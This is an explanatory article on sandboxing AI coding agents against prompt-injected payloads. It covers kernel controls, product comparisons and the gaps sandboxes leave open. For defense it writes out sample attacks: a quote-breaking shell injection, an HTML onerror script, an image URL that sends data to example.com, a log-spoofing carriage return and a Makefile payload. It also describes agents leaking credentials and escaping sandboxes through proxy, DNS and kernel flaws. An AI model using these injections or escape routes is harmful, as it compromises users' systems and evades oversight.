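NVIDIA's red team, which attacks the company's own systems to find weaknesses, reviewed an internal tool built on the PandasAI library. The team found that a user could type questions that got the model to write code that passed the filter and then ran commands on the computer. The filter examined the program's text, but much of what a Python program does is determined only when it runs. CERT Coordination Center's *PandasAI interactive prompt function can be exploited to run arbitrary Python code* (2025) adds that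 the library treated any code the agent generated as trusted, and lists versions 2.4.3 and earlier as affected.

Attempts to repair the filter failed. An outside researcher publicly reported a first problem in April 2023. NVIDIA reported more in June 2024, and in July the maintainers released changes that blocked the example exploit they had received. On 20 November they confirmed that it no longer worked. Five days later, NVIDIA sent them a new one that worked. The flaw received the identifier CVE-2024-12366 in February 2025.

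The maintainers also added security settings and an optional agent that uses a language model to check the code. NVIDIA expects attackers to get around this check too, and concludes that filtering is a useful extra layer but that "containment is the only scalable solution". Each run should have its own sandbox, so that code that passes the filter can affect only one user's session.

Unlike PandasAI, a library that accepted only a short list of table operations could have a sound checker. The rules for Codex, for instance, are written in Starlark, a restricted language that looks like Python but can't access files. But people use PandasAI because it can write any analysis they ask for, and a sound checker would refuse many of those analyses. For a tool that has to run general Python, NVIDIA's conclusion is right. The PandasAI maintainers have since released an extension that runs the generated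 code in a container, separate from the rest of the application.

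## How a sandbox contains a missed payload

A sandbox limits what a running process can reach, whereas escaping functions, filters and command checkers all work on text before anything runs. The developer sets these limits without having to decide whether the text that started the process is safe. The limits still apply after a payload has passed every filter, which is why NVIDIA recommended isolation for PandasAI.

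Computers can check what a program tries to do much more reliably than they can judge a command from its text. A program can't open a file, connect to a server or start another program without making a system call to the kernel, and Linux has only a few hundred kinds of system call. By the time the program makes the call, the shell has expanded all variables and removed all quotation marks. The commands `cat .env`, `cat .e''nv` and `cat $(echo .env)` look different to a text checker, but in each case `cat` makes a system call to open `.env`. A rule that the kernel enforces on that file therefore applies however the agent spelled the command.

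Without such rules, code that an agent writes can use whatever files, credentials and network connections its environment has, as OpenAI's *Sandbox security* warns.

### The controls and who enforces them

Landlock, a part of the Linux kernel, lets an ordinary program give up access to files. The program lists the folders it needs and what it may do in each, and the kernel blocks all other file access with a "Permission denied" error. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) describes an agent sandbox built around Landlock. Newer versions of Landlock also restrict TCP ports, signals to other processes and some local connections. Sandlock needs Linux 6.12 or later for these restrictions, and refuses to start on an older kernel instead of silently applying weaker rules.

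A mount namespace gives a process its own view of the file system. Bubblewrap, a small Linux tool that several coding agents use, can create a view in which only the project folder is writable:

```
bwrap --ro-bind / / --dev /dev --bind ~/project ~/project --unshare-net make test
```

Codex arranges its files in much the same way, according to *Codex CLI Sandbox Internals* (Vaughan, 2026). A developer can also leave a folder out of the sandbox, so that processes inside can't see that it exists.

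On macOS, the kernel enforces a profile written for a system called Seatbelt. A profile can contain rules like this one:

```
(deny file-write* (subpath "/Users/ana/project/.git/hooks"))
```

Git automatically runs scripts from this folder, so a payload that could write there might plant a script that later runs outside the sandbox. The code editor Cursor uses Seatbelt for its agents, although Apple deprecated it in 2016. Betts, Gaitonde and Haugland explain in *Implementing a secure sandbox for local agents* that the alternatives were worse. Apple's newer App Sandbox would have required Cursor to sign every program an agent might run, containers run only Linux programs, and virtual machines started too slowly and used too much memory.

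The simplest control on network access is a network namespace, which gives a process its own set of network connections. A new namespace has no connection to the outside, and the kernel enforces this isolation. The `--unshare-net` option in the command above creates one.

Many tasks need some network access, for instance to download a package. The harness can run a proxy outside the sandbox and make it the only way out. The kernel blocks direct connections, and the proxy checks each requested host against a list. In Claude Code, `curl`, `npm` and Git over HTTPS work through the proxy, but plain `ssh` and most database drivers ignore the proxy settings, so they can't connect even to an allowed host, according to Anthropic. OpenAI's policy for its own use of Codex allows expected destinations, blocks unwanted ones and requires approval for unfamiliar ones.

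A seccomp filter tells the Linux kernel which system calls to refuse. It can stop a process from mounting a disk or loading a kernel module, and it reduces the kernel code a payload can attack. It can't protect a particular file, because it can read only the memory address of the file's name, not the name itself.

The kernel can also pause a system call and pass it to a supervisor, a separate program that can read the name or address from memory. But another part of the process may change that memory after the check. To prevent this when a process tries to connect to a server, Sandlock's supervisor copies the address, checks the copy and opens the connection itself.

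Two further Linux features control privileges. The `no_new_privs` flag stops a process from gaining rights by starting a program such as `sudo`, and no process can remove the flag once it is set. A user namespace gives a process administrator rights that count only inside the namespace, which lets an ordinary user create the other kinds of namespace. Some Linux systems restrict user namespaces. According to OpenAI's *Sandbox*, users of Ubuntu 24.04 may have to load an extra security profile before bubblewrap works.

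Limits on time and memory stop a payload from exhausting the computer's resources. The harness can stop a command after a fixed time, and a kernel feature called cgroups can cap the memory and number of processes for a whole group of processes. Sandlock doesn't use cgroups. Instead, its supervisor counts the memory and processes a program requests. Wang and Zheng consider this sufficient for buggy code, but say cgroups are stronger against deliberate attacks.

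### Why child processes inherit the limits

A new Linux process inherits its parent's namespaces, Landlock rules, seccomp filters and `no_new_privs` flag, and keeps them when it loads a different program. A process can add Landlock rules or seccomp filters, but it can't remove any. A Seatbelt profile likewise covers every descendant of the first process.

A command checker that approves `make test` does not inspect the commands in the project's Makefile, but a sandbox applies the same limits to those commands as to `make` itself. OpenAI says that Codex's sandbox limits also apply to Git, package managers and test runners, and Anthropic notes that Claude Code's sandbox still applies even if an approved command does more than its name suggests.

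A process inherits the sandbox's limits from the process that starts it, so a program that was already running outside the sandbox doesn't have them, even if it acts on a request from inside.

### A sandbox step by step

Su and Wen (2026), in *Learning CLI Agents with Structured Action Credit under Selective Observation*, trained agents to work on files by writing shell commands. Their sandbox for these commands needs neither Docker nor administrator rights. Let P be the running command with all its descendants, W the working folder for the task, and R a fixed set of system folders. The sandbox is supposed to guarantee:

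```
writes(P) ⊆ W
reads(P)  ⊆ W ∪ R
net(P)    = ∅
time(P)   ≤ 10 seconds
```

The first two lines say that P can write only in W and read only in W or R. The third says that it has no network access. The harness sets this up for each command as follows:

1. A text filter rejects commands that match patterns for deleting whole folders or for a fork bomb, a program that endlessly starts copies of itself.
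2. A launcher starts a new process with `unshare`, in new user and network namespaces. Its standard input comes from `/dev/null`, which is always empty, so no command can hang while waiting for someone to type.
3. The new process sets `no_new_privs`. Linux requires this before a process without administrator rights may restrict itself with Landlock.
4. The process checks which version of Landlock the kernel has and installs its rules. In R, it may read files, list folders and run programs. In W, it may also write, create and remove files.
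5. The process moves to W and starts `/bin/bash`, which parses the agent's command.
6. A watchdog outside the sandbox collects the output. If the command is still running after 10 seconds, the watchdog ends the whole session, meaning the group of processes that began with this command.

All the kernel's limits are in place before Bash reads any of the agent's text, so nothing in the text can prevent them from taking effect.

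The design is sound, but the guarantees are slightly too strong. The `setsid` command starts a new session, so a payload could use it to escape the watchdog and run for longer than 10 seconds, though it still couldn't access the network or extra files. Bubblewrap can prevent this with a process namespace, because the kernel kills everything in the namespace when its first process ends.

The published list of file rights also omits truncation, which Landlock has treated as a separate right since its third version. If the rules don't restrict truncation, a payload can empty a file outside W even though it can't write to it. Landlock also doesn't control changes to file permissions, so a payload could use `chmod` to make the user's other files unreadable.

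The text filter in step 1 is the weakest part, for the same reasons text filters usually are. It partly makes up for the lack of limits on memory and the number of processes, but a cgroup would limit both better.

Strict rules can also break ordinary commands. Taken literally, these rules block writes to `/dev/null`, where shell scripts routinely send unwanted output. Wang and Zheng found that most of the work in getting build tools to run in Sandlock was granting access to `/dev/null` and temporary folders.

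### The notification payload with and without the sandbox

Consider the original notification harness again, with a message that tries to leave a file in the user's home folder:

```
done'; echo INJECTED > ~/marker.txt #
```

The harness inserts it into the template without escaping, and the shell receives this line:

```
notify-send 'Agent' 'done'; echo INJECTED > ~/marker.txt #'
```

Without a sandbox, the shell runs `notify-send`, then creates `marker.txt` and writes INJECTED in it.

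With Su and Wen's sandbox, the shell parses the line in exactly the same way, so the injection still succeeds. The shell then asks the kernel to create a file in the home folder. The home folder is not in W, so the kernel refuses:

```
/bin/bash: line 1: /home/ana/marker.txt: Permission denied
```

The earlier payload, `echo INJECTED`, would print its word in both cases, because printing needs no file or network access.

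The table lists what any other command in place of `echo` could do, assuming that the sandbox restricts truncation.

| | Without the sandbox | With the sandbox |
|---|---|---|
| Read | Every file the user can read, including saved passwords and SSH keys | Files in W and R, and any environment variables the harness passes on |
| Write | Every file the user can change | Files in W |
| Send | Anything it has read, to any computer the user's machine can reach | Nothing over the network; its printed output goes back to the harness |
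| Run | Any program, for as long as it likes | Programs in W and R, under the same limits, for 10 seconds unless it uses `setsid` |

How much protection this gives depends largely on W. A notification needs no project files, so the harness could use an empty temporary folder and leave a payload almost nothing to damage. A coding agent needs the project itself, which a payload could then read and change.

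Network namespaces don't block local connections through sockets that have a file path, such as the one `notify-send` uses to reach the desktop. The notification appears only if the desktop accepts a connection from another user namespace.

### Containers, gVisor, virtual machines and WebAssembly

Landlock, seccomp and namespaces all rely on the host's kernel, so a payload that exploits a flaw in that kernel may escape all of them at once. A container combines namespaces and resource limits with its own set of program files, but it has the same weakness because it shares the host's kernel. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026) points out that one kernel flaw is enough to escape a container.

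gVisor puts a second kernel in between. This is an ordinary program, written in Go, that answers most of the container's system calls itself and makes only a limited set of calls to the real kernel. A microVM, a small virtual machine with few simulated devices, goes further by running a complete Linux kernel of its own, which the processor's hardware separates from the host. A payload that takes over this kernel still has to break out through the monitor, the program that runs the virtual machine. Firecracker is a widely used monitor of this kind.

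WebAssembly is a portable code format that developers can compile programs into. A runtime executes each program in its own region of memory, and the program can call only the functions that the runtime provides. *Abstraction of Trusted Execution Environments as the Missing Layer* (2025) describes WebAssembly as nearly as fast as ordinary programs and recommends it for untrusted code. However, if a complex application depends closely on one operating system, only a virtual machine can package it unchanged. WebAssembly therefore suits a small calculation that an agent has written, but not a typical project with its own compiler, package manager and test programs.

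In *AI Code Sandboxes*, Andronchik and Lokhmakov (2026) compared five products on one server. They checked whether code inside each sandbox could reach 14 kernel functions, devices and files that past attacks had used. They also ran 28 tests for details about the host, such as its processor model and the serial numbers of its disks.

| Product | Type | Attack routes reachable, of 14 | Host details exposed, of 28 |
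|---|---|---|---|
| E2B | MicroVM (Firecracker) | 7 | 0 |
| microsandbox | MicroVM | 11 | 0 |
| Arrakis | MicroVM | 12 | 1 |
| gVisor | Second kernel | 5 | 2 |
| Daytona | Container | 11 | 10 |

The third column makes microVMs look weaker than they are. In a microVM, the payload usually reaches functions in the virtual machine's own kernel, so exploiting them doesn't give access to the host. Daytona is also not a typical container, because it runs in Docker's "privileged" mode, which switches off several protections, including the seccomp filter.

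The number of different system calls that can reach the host's kernel is a better measure of the remaining risk. Firecracker's filter allows 55 and gVisor's allows 84, while Docker's standard filter for containers allows 361 without conditions.

A sandbox's security depends on updates as well as design. Andronchik and Lokhmakov found that the default version of Firecracker in self-hosted E2B had not changed for 399 days, so a Firecracker fix may take a long time to reach people who host E2B themselves.

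Stronger isolation usually takes longer to start. Wang and Zheng, who developed Sandlock, timed a simple `echo` command in it at about 6 milliseconds, of which the sandbox added about 5. Docker took 44 times as long. They tested only these two, so their startup figures for the other types in this table are rough guides.

| Type | What a payload must break to escape | Startup | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|---|
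| Process sandbox | The host's kernel or the sandbox's rules | 6 ms (Sandlock), 30 ms (bubblewrap) | Shares the host's kernel |
| Container | The host's kernel or the container's settings | 300 ms (Docker without administrator rights) | Shares the host's kernel; needs its own program files |
| gVisor | gVisor, then the host's kernel | 200 ms | Slower file access; some programs don't work |
| MicroVM | Its own kernel, then the monitor | 100 ms (Firecracker) | Needs memory for a second system |
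| WebAssembly | The runtime | No comparable figure | Programs must be compiled for it |

*Tracekit Box* (2026), which describes a sandbox that gives every job its own virtual machine, puts Firecracker's startup time somewhat higher, in the low hundreds of milliseconds.

Sandboxes can also slow programs after startup. In Wang and Zheng's tests, the database Redis ran at normal speed in Sandlock but at about 76 percent of normal speed in Docker. Sandlock was slower than Docker when its supervisor had to handle each network message, which raised the time for a short exchange from 20 to 55 microseconds. *Caging the Agents* (2026) reports that gVisor slowed file reading by 20 to 40 percent in a healthcare company's agents and added 2 to 5 milliseconds to each new connection. The model took 500 to 3,000 milliseconds to respond, so users would hardly notice these delays.

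Startup time matters if every command gets a new sandbox, but much less if one sandbox lasts for a whole session. A service can also start sandboxes in advance and hand them out when needed.

The right sandbox depends on whose code might run. A process sandbox is reasonable for one developer's laptop, where commands are short and the main risks are mistakes and the occasional hidden instruction. A company that runs strangers' code on shared servers should use microVMs, and Wang and Zheng agree that their tool is not meant for that use. In *SideKernel*, Prasakis (2026) also ranks microVMs above containers, but declines to rank them against Seatbelt because the answer depends on the kind of attack.

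### What coding agents do by default

In late 2026, the makers of the main coding agents still disagree about whether to turn the sandbox on for everyone. The table shows the settings for commands run on the user's own computer.

| Agent | Sandbox by default | File access in the sandbox | Network access in the sandbox |
|---|---|---|---|
| Codex | On | Reads almost everything; writes in the project and temporary folders | Off |
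| Zed | On | Writes only in the project, and not to `.git` | Off |
| Cursor | On for commands that run without approval | Depends on the project's and administrator's settings | Off |
| Claude Code | Off | Reads almost everything; writes in the project and a temporary folder | Approved hosts only |
| GitHub Copilot | Off | Depends on the user's or company's policy | Depends on the policy |
| Gemini CLI | Off | On macOS, reads broadly; writes in the project | On macOS, unrestricted |

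Under the defaults listed in OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, `.git` and Codex's own settings folder stay read-only inside the project. Codex recommends a read-only mode for folders that aren't under version control. OpenAI confirms that the default mode can read files almost anywhere, so the sandbox protects most private files from being changed but not from being read.

Zed, a code editor, applies similar limits to its agent's terminal and web-fetching tools. The agent can ask the user for more access, but never for permission to write to `.git`. According to *Agent Sandboxing*, Cursor chose a sandbox over very detailed lists of allowed commands, and users can still choose to approve every action themselves.

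In Claude Code, the user has to turn the sandbox on with the command `/sandbox`. If the sandbox can't start, Claude Code runs commands without it by default, though a setting makes it exit instead. Claude Code has no sandbox for commands that run directly on Windows, but Codex does.

GitHub (2026) released its local sandbox for Copilot as a public preview in June, and users enable it for each session. Google's *Sandboxing in Gemini CLI* lists many sandbox options, including containers and gVisor. The default profile on macOS restricts writing but lets a payload read private files and send them anywhere. *Hands-on with Antigravity CLI*, Google's tutorial for another of its agents, shows the sandbox as off in the settings list.

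Cloud versions are stricter because the maker controls the computer. Codex in the cloud has network access and the user's secrets while it installs a project's software. It then removes the secrets and, by default, disconnects from the internet before the agent starts work.

Sandboxes also reduce interruptions, because the harness doesn't need to ask before running a command that can't do much harm. Anthropic reports 84 percent fewer permission prompts in internal use of its sandbox. Betts and colleagues report that sandboxed agents at Cursor stopped 40 percent less often than unsandboxed ones. The two companies counted different things, so these figures don't show which sandbox is better. Fewer prompts probably also improve safety, because users check each prompt less carefully as the number of prompts grows.

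Many people still run coding agents without a sandbox. Betts and colleagues report that about a third of Cursor requests on supported systems use one. In a survey by Prasakis, fewer than 40 percent of the 68 respondents who used coding agents ran them in a sandbox. The survey was informal and drew on Prasakis's professional and university contacts, who may know more about security than most users.

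## What a sandbox leaves exposed

To fix a failing test, an agent needs the project's files, usually some packages from the internet, and a way to hand back its changes. A sandbox that withheld all of these would be very safe, but the agent could not fix the test. *Tracekit Box* points out that an agent can do harm with the same access it needs for its job, and a payload running in the sandbox has that access too.

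### Damage within the rules

Suppose an attacker injects the command `echo INJECTED > main.py` into a coding agent's sandbox. The project folder is writable, so the kernel lets the shell replace the contents of `main.py` with one word. If the sandbox keeps the `.git` folder read-only, the user can restore the last committed version but loses any later work. OpenAI advises Codex users to commit often, which limits the loss.

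An agent can do similar damage with no attacker involved. In an example from *SABER* (2026), a safety benchmark for coding agents, one tool moves files within the limits of the task and another deletes a shared cache folder. Both look plausible, and the container allows them.

Agents that try to be careful can also misjudge what a sandbox covers. *V³AST-Bench* (2026) asked agents to rename some data files with a supplied program that also wrote ten junk files into the project. One agent tried the program on copies in a temporary folder, but the program had the project's real path built in, so it still wrote the junk files into the project. In another run, the agent gave the program a different root folder, saw the junk files appear there, and then renamed the data files itself.

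Secrets inside a sandbox are exposed even if it has no network access. NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* reports that the company's red team could often get credentials out of agents in such sandboxes through the chat window. The agents read the credentials from their environment and included them in their replies. This matters most when colleagues or strangers can also talk to the agent, and most of the agents in those tests were connected to chat services. On a private laptop, only the user sees the reply, but the secret has still gone to the model's provider.

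By default, commands in Anthropic's sandbox for Claude Code can read the user's SSH keys and inherit all environment variables, including any that contain access tokens. Users can block particular credentials, or mask them so that commands receive a dummy value and the proxy inserts the real one into outgoing requests.

Some files are harder to hide because a program in the sandbox needs them. *The Compiler May Read It, the Agent May Not* (2026) considers a project in which the compiler has to read source files that the agent must not see. File-level access controls cannot distinguish the compiler's reads from the agent's. If the agent can edit the build instructions, it can also make the build print the protected file.

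### Allowed hosts and tools with their own credentials

In an example from OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, a user asks Codex to fix a reported bug, and the report contains a command that sends the latest commit to an outside server. A list of allowed hosts stops this if the server isn't on it. But OpenAI's preset list for downloading packages has 71 entries, including `github.com`, `google.com` and `azure.com`, where attackers can have accounts too. The developer Simon Willison warned in June 2025 that any of the 71 might offer a way to send data out.

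Codex can also restrict requests to methods that normally only fetch data. This blocks the upload in OpenAI's example, but a request that fetches a page can still carry a secret in its URL.

Anthropic gives a similar warning about allowing `github.com` in Claude Code. Claude Code's proxy also relies on the host name that the program supplies and doesn't inspect encrypted traffic, so a program may be able to reach hosts that aren't on the allowed list. A company can install its own proxy to decrypt and inspect the traffic. Even then, an allowed server may pass data on to one that isn't allowed. *Sandbox vulnerability gives rogue AI agents a path to escape* (Smalley, 2026) illustrates this risk with research on another company's sandbox.

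Some sandboxes don't try to stop leaks. *Deliberately exposed and out of scope*, from the documentation of an open-source container setup for Claude Code, explains that the setup's network rules protect other computers on the internal network but leave the internet open "so Claude works". This is reasonable if the project is public and the container holds no secrets.

Agents can also act through tools that run outside the sandbox. Suppose a harness offers an email tool and stores the mail password outside the sandbox. A payload in the sandbox can't read the password or call the tool, but its output goes back to the model. If the output contains an instruction to send an email and the model follows it, the harness sends the email from the user's account. The sandbox doesn't prevent this, because no process inside it contacts the mail server.

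Many such tools use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to other software. OpenAI notes that remote MCP tools connect from its own service, so firewall rules around the developer's sandbox don't cover them. Codex always asks for approval before it calls a tool marked as destructive, but this depends on the tool's developer marking it. A safer email tool would have credentials that only let it save drafts.

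### Delayed execution

A payload can also write a file that someone runs later, outside the sandbox. For example, it could add a line to the project's Makefile:

```
test:
	python3 -m pytest
	echo INJECTED
```

The new line runs under the sandbox's limits when the agent runs `make test`, but with all the user's rights if the user later runs the same command in an ordinary terminal. The sandbox has worked as designed, because it was supposed to let the agent edit the project.

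Pillar Security published research on this problem in July 2026. Miner (2026), in *The Agent Stayed in the Sandbox. The Command Still Ran*, explains that the agent only wrote a file, which a trusted program then ran. Fadilpašić (2026), in *Top AI coding agents can be easy victims to sandbox escapes*, also traces the risk to programs outside the sandbox that read what the agent writes.

Many kinds of file can carry a delayed payload:

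| File | What runs it outside the sandbox |
|---|---|
| Makefile or other build script | The user's next build or test |
| Git hook | Git, for example at the next commit |
| Editor task or extension settings | The editor, sometimes as soon as it opens the project |
| Hook or MCP settings for the agent | The harness, often at its next start |
| Workflow file for a build server | The server, after the next upload of code |
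| Shell startup file, such as `.zshrc` | The next terminal window |

NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*, published in January 2026, lists three mandatory controls: restricting network access, blocking writes outside the project, and blocking the agent from writing to any configuration file, even inside the project. The user can't approve exceptions to the last control and has to edit configuration files by hand. It also covers instruction files such as `CLAUDE.md`, which contain no program but influence what the agent does in later sessions. If someone commits a malicious hook setting to a shared repository, it can affect everyone who copies the project.

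Codex keeps `.git`, its own settings folder and its `.agents` folder read-only. Anthropic's separate sandbox runtime can enclose all of Claude Code, and it blocks writes to Git hooks, shell startup files and several of Claude Code's own settings. On macOS, it applies these rules at each write. On Linux, it lists the protected files once, at launch, so the list doesn't cover a repository that the agent creates or downloads later. Anthropic therefore tells Linux users to review anything new after an unattended session.

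Two flaws from early 2026 show how easily a sandbox can miss one of these files. According to INCIBE's *CVE-2026-25725* (2026), Claude Code didn't protect its `settings.json` file if the file didn't exist at startup. Malicious code in the sandbox could create the file and add hooks, which Claude Code would run outside the sandbox after a restart. Anthropic fixed this in version 2.1.2. According to INCIBE's *CVE-2026-26268* (2026), the editor Cursor didn't sufficiently protect Git's settings and hooks. The user didn't have to do anything unusual to trigger a hook. Version 2.5 fixed the flaw, which has a severity score of 8.0.

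Read-only settings don't solve the Makefile problem, because a coding agent often has good reason to edit build files. Someone will also later run the program it is working on. NVIDIA's later guide recommends that agents write only to locations where nothing is run, which suits an agent that writes reports but not one that writes software. For code, the user can read the changes before running them, starting with the build files, or keep running the project in a sandbox. A build server should test unreviewed changes in a separate sandbox that has no access to the passwords the server uses to publish releases.

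### Output that leaves the sandbox

A browser or terminal outside the sandbox doesn't have the sandbox's limits. Suppose a test program in the sandbox writes its results as a web page, and one of the tests has this name:

```
<img src="x" onerror="alert('INJECTED')">
```

In the sandbox, the name is only text in a file. When the user opens the report, the browser parses the text as HTML and runs the script. If the harness serves the report from the same web address as its control page, the script may also be able to send commands to the harness as the logged-in user.

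The test program should have escaped the name, but a payload in the sandbox could have changed the program or the finished report, so the escaping has to happen outside the sandbox. The sandbox can return the results as JSON, and the harness can then build the page and apply `html.escape` to each name.

If the harness has to show a complete page from the sandbox, it can put the page in a restricted frame:

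```
<iframe sandbox src="report.html"></iframe>
```

The `sandbox` attribute makes the browser refuse to run scripts in the frame. It doesn't stop the browser from loading images, such as this one:

```
<img src="https://example.com/log?note=INJECTED">
```

When the report opens, the browser requests this address, and `example.com` receives the word INJECTED. A payload could send a secret instead, and it would leave through the user's browser even though the sandbox has no network access. *Hardening LLM-based Applications* (2025) summarises advice from NVIDIA's red team to sanitise or disable images and links in model output for this reason. The harness can also send the page with a content security policy, which can stop the browser from loading images from other sites. Links still need to be sanitised or disabled, since a user may click one.

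Log files can mislead a user in a terminal. Suppose the sandboxed tests write `3 tests failed` to a log, followed by a carriage return and `all tests pass`. If the user displays the log with `cat test.log`, the second text overwrites the first, which has the same length, and the terminal shows only this:

```
all tests pass
```

With `cat -v test.log`, the carriage return appears as `^M`:

```
3 tests failed^Mall tests pass
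```

`cat -v` also garbles accented letters, so a harness that displays logs should use a function that changes only control characters. It should apply this function when it displays the text, because a payload in the sandbox could undo any earlier cleaning of the file.

### Flaws in the sandbox

In 2025, Codex had a sandbox flaw that came from trusting the model's output. According to NIST's *CVE-2025-59532 Detail*, versions 0.2.0 to 0.38.0 could accept a working folder that the model chose and make it writable, even if it was outside the user's project. The model could therefore move the sandbox's boundary. The block on network access still worked. CERT.hr's *CVE-2025-59532* reports that version 0.39.0 fixed the flaw by setting the boundary from the folder where the user started the session.

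Another flaw arose because Claude Code's sandbox covers shell commands but not its built-in tools for editing files. *Claude Code below 2.1.251 let code in its Bash sandbox* (rulestack, 2026) reports that on macOS, sandboxed code could redirect an edit to a file outside the project, a flaw fixed in version 2.1.251. The University of Vermont notes more generally that shell commands and file tools reach the same files by different routes, so a control on one doesn't automatically cover the other.

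Users can avoid this split by putting the whole harness in a container or virtual machine, but the harness's login details are then usually inside it too. OpenAI warns that if Codex runs in a development container with its own sandbox off, a malicious project can steal anything in the container, including Codex's credentials.

A flaw in the host's kernel can defeat correct rules, so NVIDIA recommends a virtual machine. But a virtual machine doesn't help much if it can access too many of the host's files. SC Media UK's *AI agent escapes VM sandbox via Linux zero-day vulnerability* reports that researchers at Accomplish AI used a Linux kernel flaw to get Anthropic's Claude Cowork agent out of a virtual machine on a Mac. Linux developers fixed the flaw in mid-June 2026. The researchers also advised users to restrict the agent's access to folders, which suggests the shared folders were part of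 the problem.

The proxy that filters network traffic is also software with flaws. OpenAI (2026) disclosed that models in a security test reached the internet by exploiting a previously unknown flaw in a package proxy, the only network service their sandbox was meant to let them use. Fortune (2026) reports that the proxy's maker, JFrog, has fixed the flaw. *Tracekit Box* mentions another OpenAI agent that got out through DNS, which translates host names into addresses, because the network filter didn't cover it. NVIDIA recommends allowing DNS requests only to trusted servers.

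### Wrong settings and switched-off sandboxes

A single setting can remove most of a sandbox's protection. Anthropic gives the example of allowing access to Docker's control socket, which programs use to start containers. Docker runs outside the sandbox, usually with administrator rights, so access to the socket effectively gives access to the whole computer. Claude Code's `enableWeakerNestedSandbox` option lets its sandbox run inside an ordinary container but weakens the sandbox considerably. Anthropic recommends this option only where something else provides the isolation.

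Mistakes in a settings file can go unnoticed because the agent still works. Anthropic's sandbox runtime refuses to start if the file is invalid, but if the default file is missing, it starts with strict built-in rules. A user can check the limits with a harmless command. For Codex on Linux, this one should fail when run from a project folder:

```
codex sandbox linux touch ~/marker.txt
```

If `marker.txt` appears in the home folder, the sandbox isn't protecting it.

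Users can also switch off the protection. Codex's `--yolo` option removes both the sandbox and the approval prompts. Claude Code's `--dangerously-skip-permissions` removes most prompts, and Anthropic says to use it only inside a container, a virtual machine or the sandbox runtime. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026) tested what such bypass modes allow in Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI. In default mode, Codex's sandbox and Claude Code's approval prompt stopped a write outside the project, but in bypass mode nothing checked shell commands. Gemini CLI's file tool still checked the path in bypass mode, but the model used the shell to write outside the project in all five runs. All three agents could also change their own settings in bypass mode, so one unprotected session may weaken later ones.

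Claude Code can also run a command outside the sandbox with the user's approval. If a command fails because of the sandbox, the agent may ask to rerun that one command outside it. An attacker could write a payload that deliberately fails in the sandbox, hoping that a tired user will approve the rerun. Setting `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to `false` removes this option.

### The objection that strict limits stop useful work

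People mostly switch off sandboxes because the limits interfere with their work. In the forum thread *Codex cloud agent unable to install pnpm dependencies*, one user reported that none of their JavaScript projects worked in Codex because the container had no internet connection after setup. Another got a project to install by skipping the packages' installation scripts. In *Codex scheme for operations requiring secret access after "setup" runs*, a user called the removal of secrets after setup an "almost immediate blocker" for projects that depend on private packages. Anthropic says some tools don't work in a sandbox at all, including Docker and the file-watching program `watchman`.

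These drawbacks matter because a sandbox protects nobody if people turn it off. OpenAI responded to the first complaint by letting users configure network access. A short list of allowed hosts is enough for most package downloads. Codex's network proxy blocks private addresses by default, but users can add an exception for one internal service. A company can go further and allow packages only from a repository that it checks, as NVIDIA recommends. This also protects against some malicious packages that a general list of package sites would let through.

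NVIDIA suggests four levels of access:

1. Nobody can override the company's list of forbidden files.
2. The agent can read and write freely in the project, except for configuration files.
3. The company allows specific exceptions, such as reading one SSH key.
4. Everything else needs the user's approval.

NVIDIA says the harness should ask for approval every time, because an attacker could exploit a remembered approval. Claude Code can remember an approved host. NVIDIA's rule is safer for a rare action such as editing a shell startup file. But a package site that an agent contacts fifty times a day belongs on the third level, because asking every time would produce too many prompts.

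Private packages and services need credentials, which a credential broker outside the sandbox can add to approved requests. In Claude Code's cloud version, for example, a proxy outside the sandbox holds the user's GitHub token. A payload can't steal the token, but it can still make any request that the broker approves, so the token should cover only the current task and expire soon afterwards. The user who complained about private packages proposed a fixed installation script that the agent could start, with only the script having access to the secret. This would work, but the script should skip the packages' own installation scripts, or a malicious package could read the secret.

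Disposable workspaces limit how much a payload can find or leave behind. The harness copies the project into a new sandbox, lets the agent work there, copies out the changes and deletes the rest. NVIDIA recommends either a new sandbox for each task or regular rebuilding, such as weekly for a virtual machine. Old sandboxes accumulate passwords, code from other projects and possibly a payload set to run during the next task. A new sandbox needs the project's packages installed again, though a prepared image with the usual packages saves most of that time. The copied changes can still contain a delayed payload, so someone has to review them before they run elsewhere.
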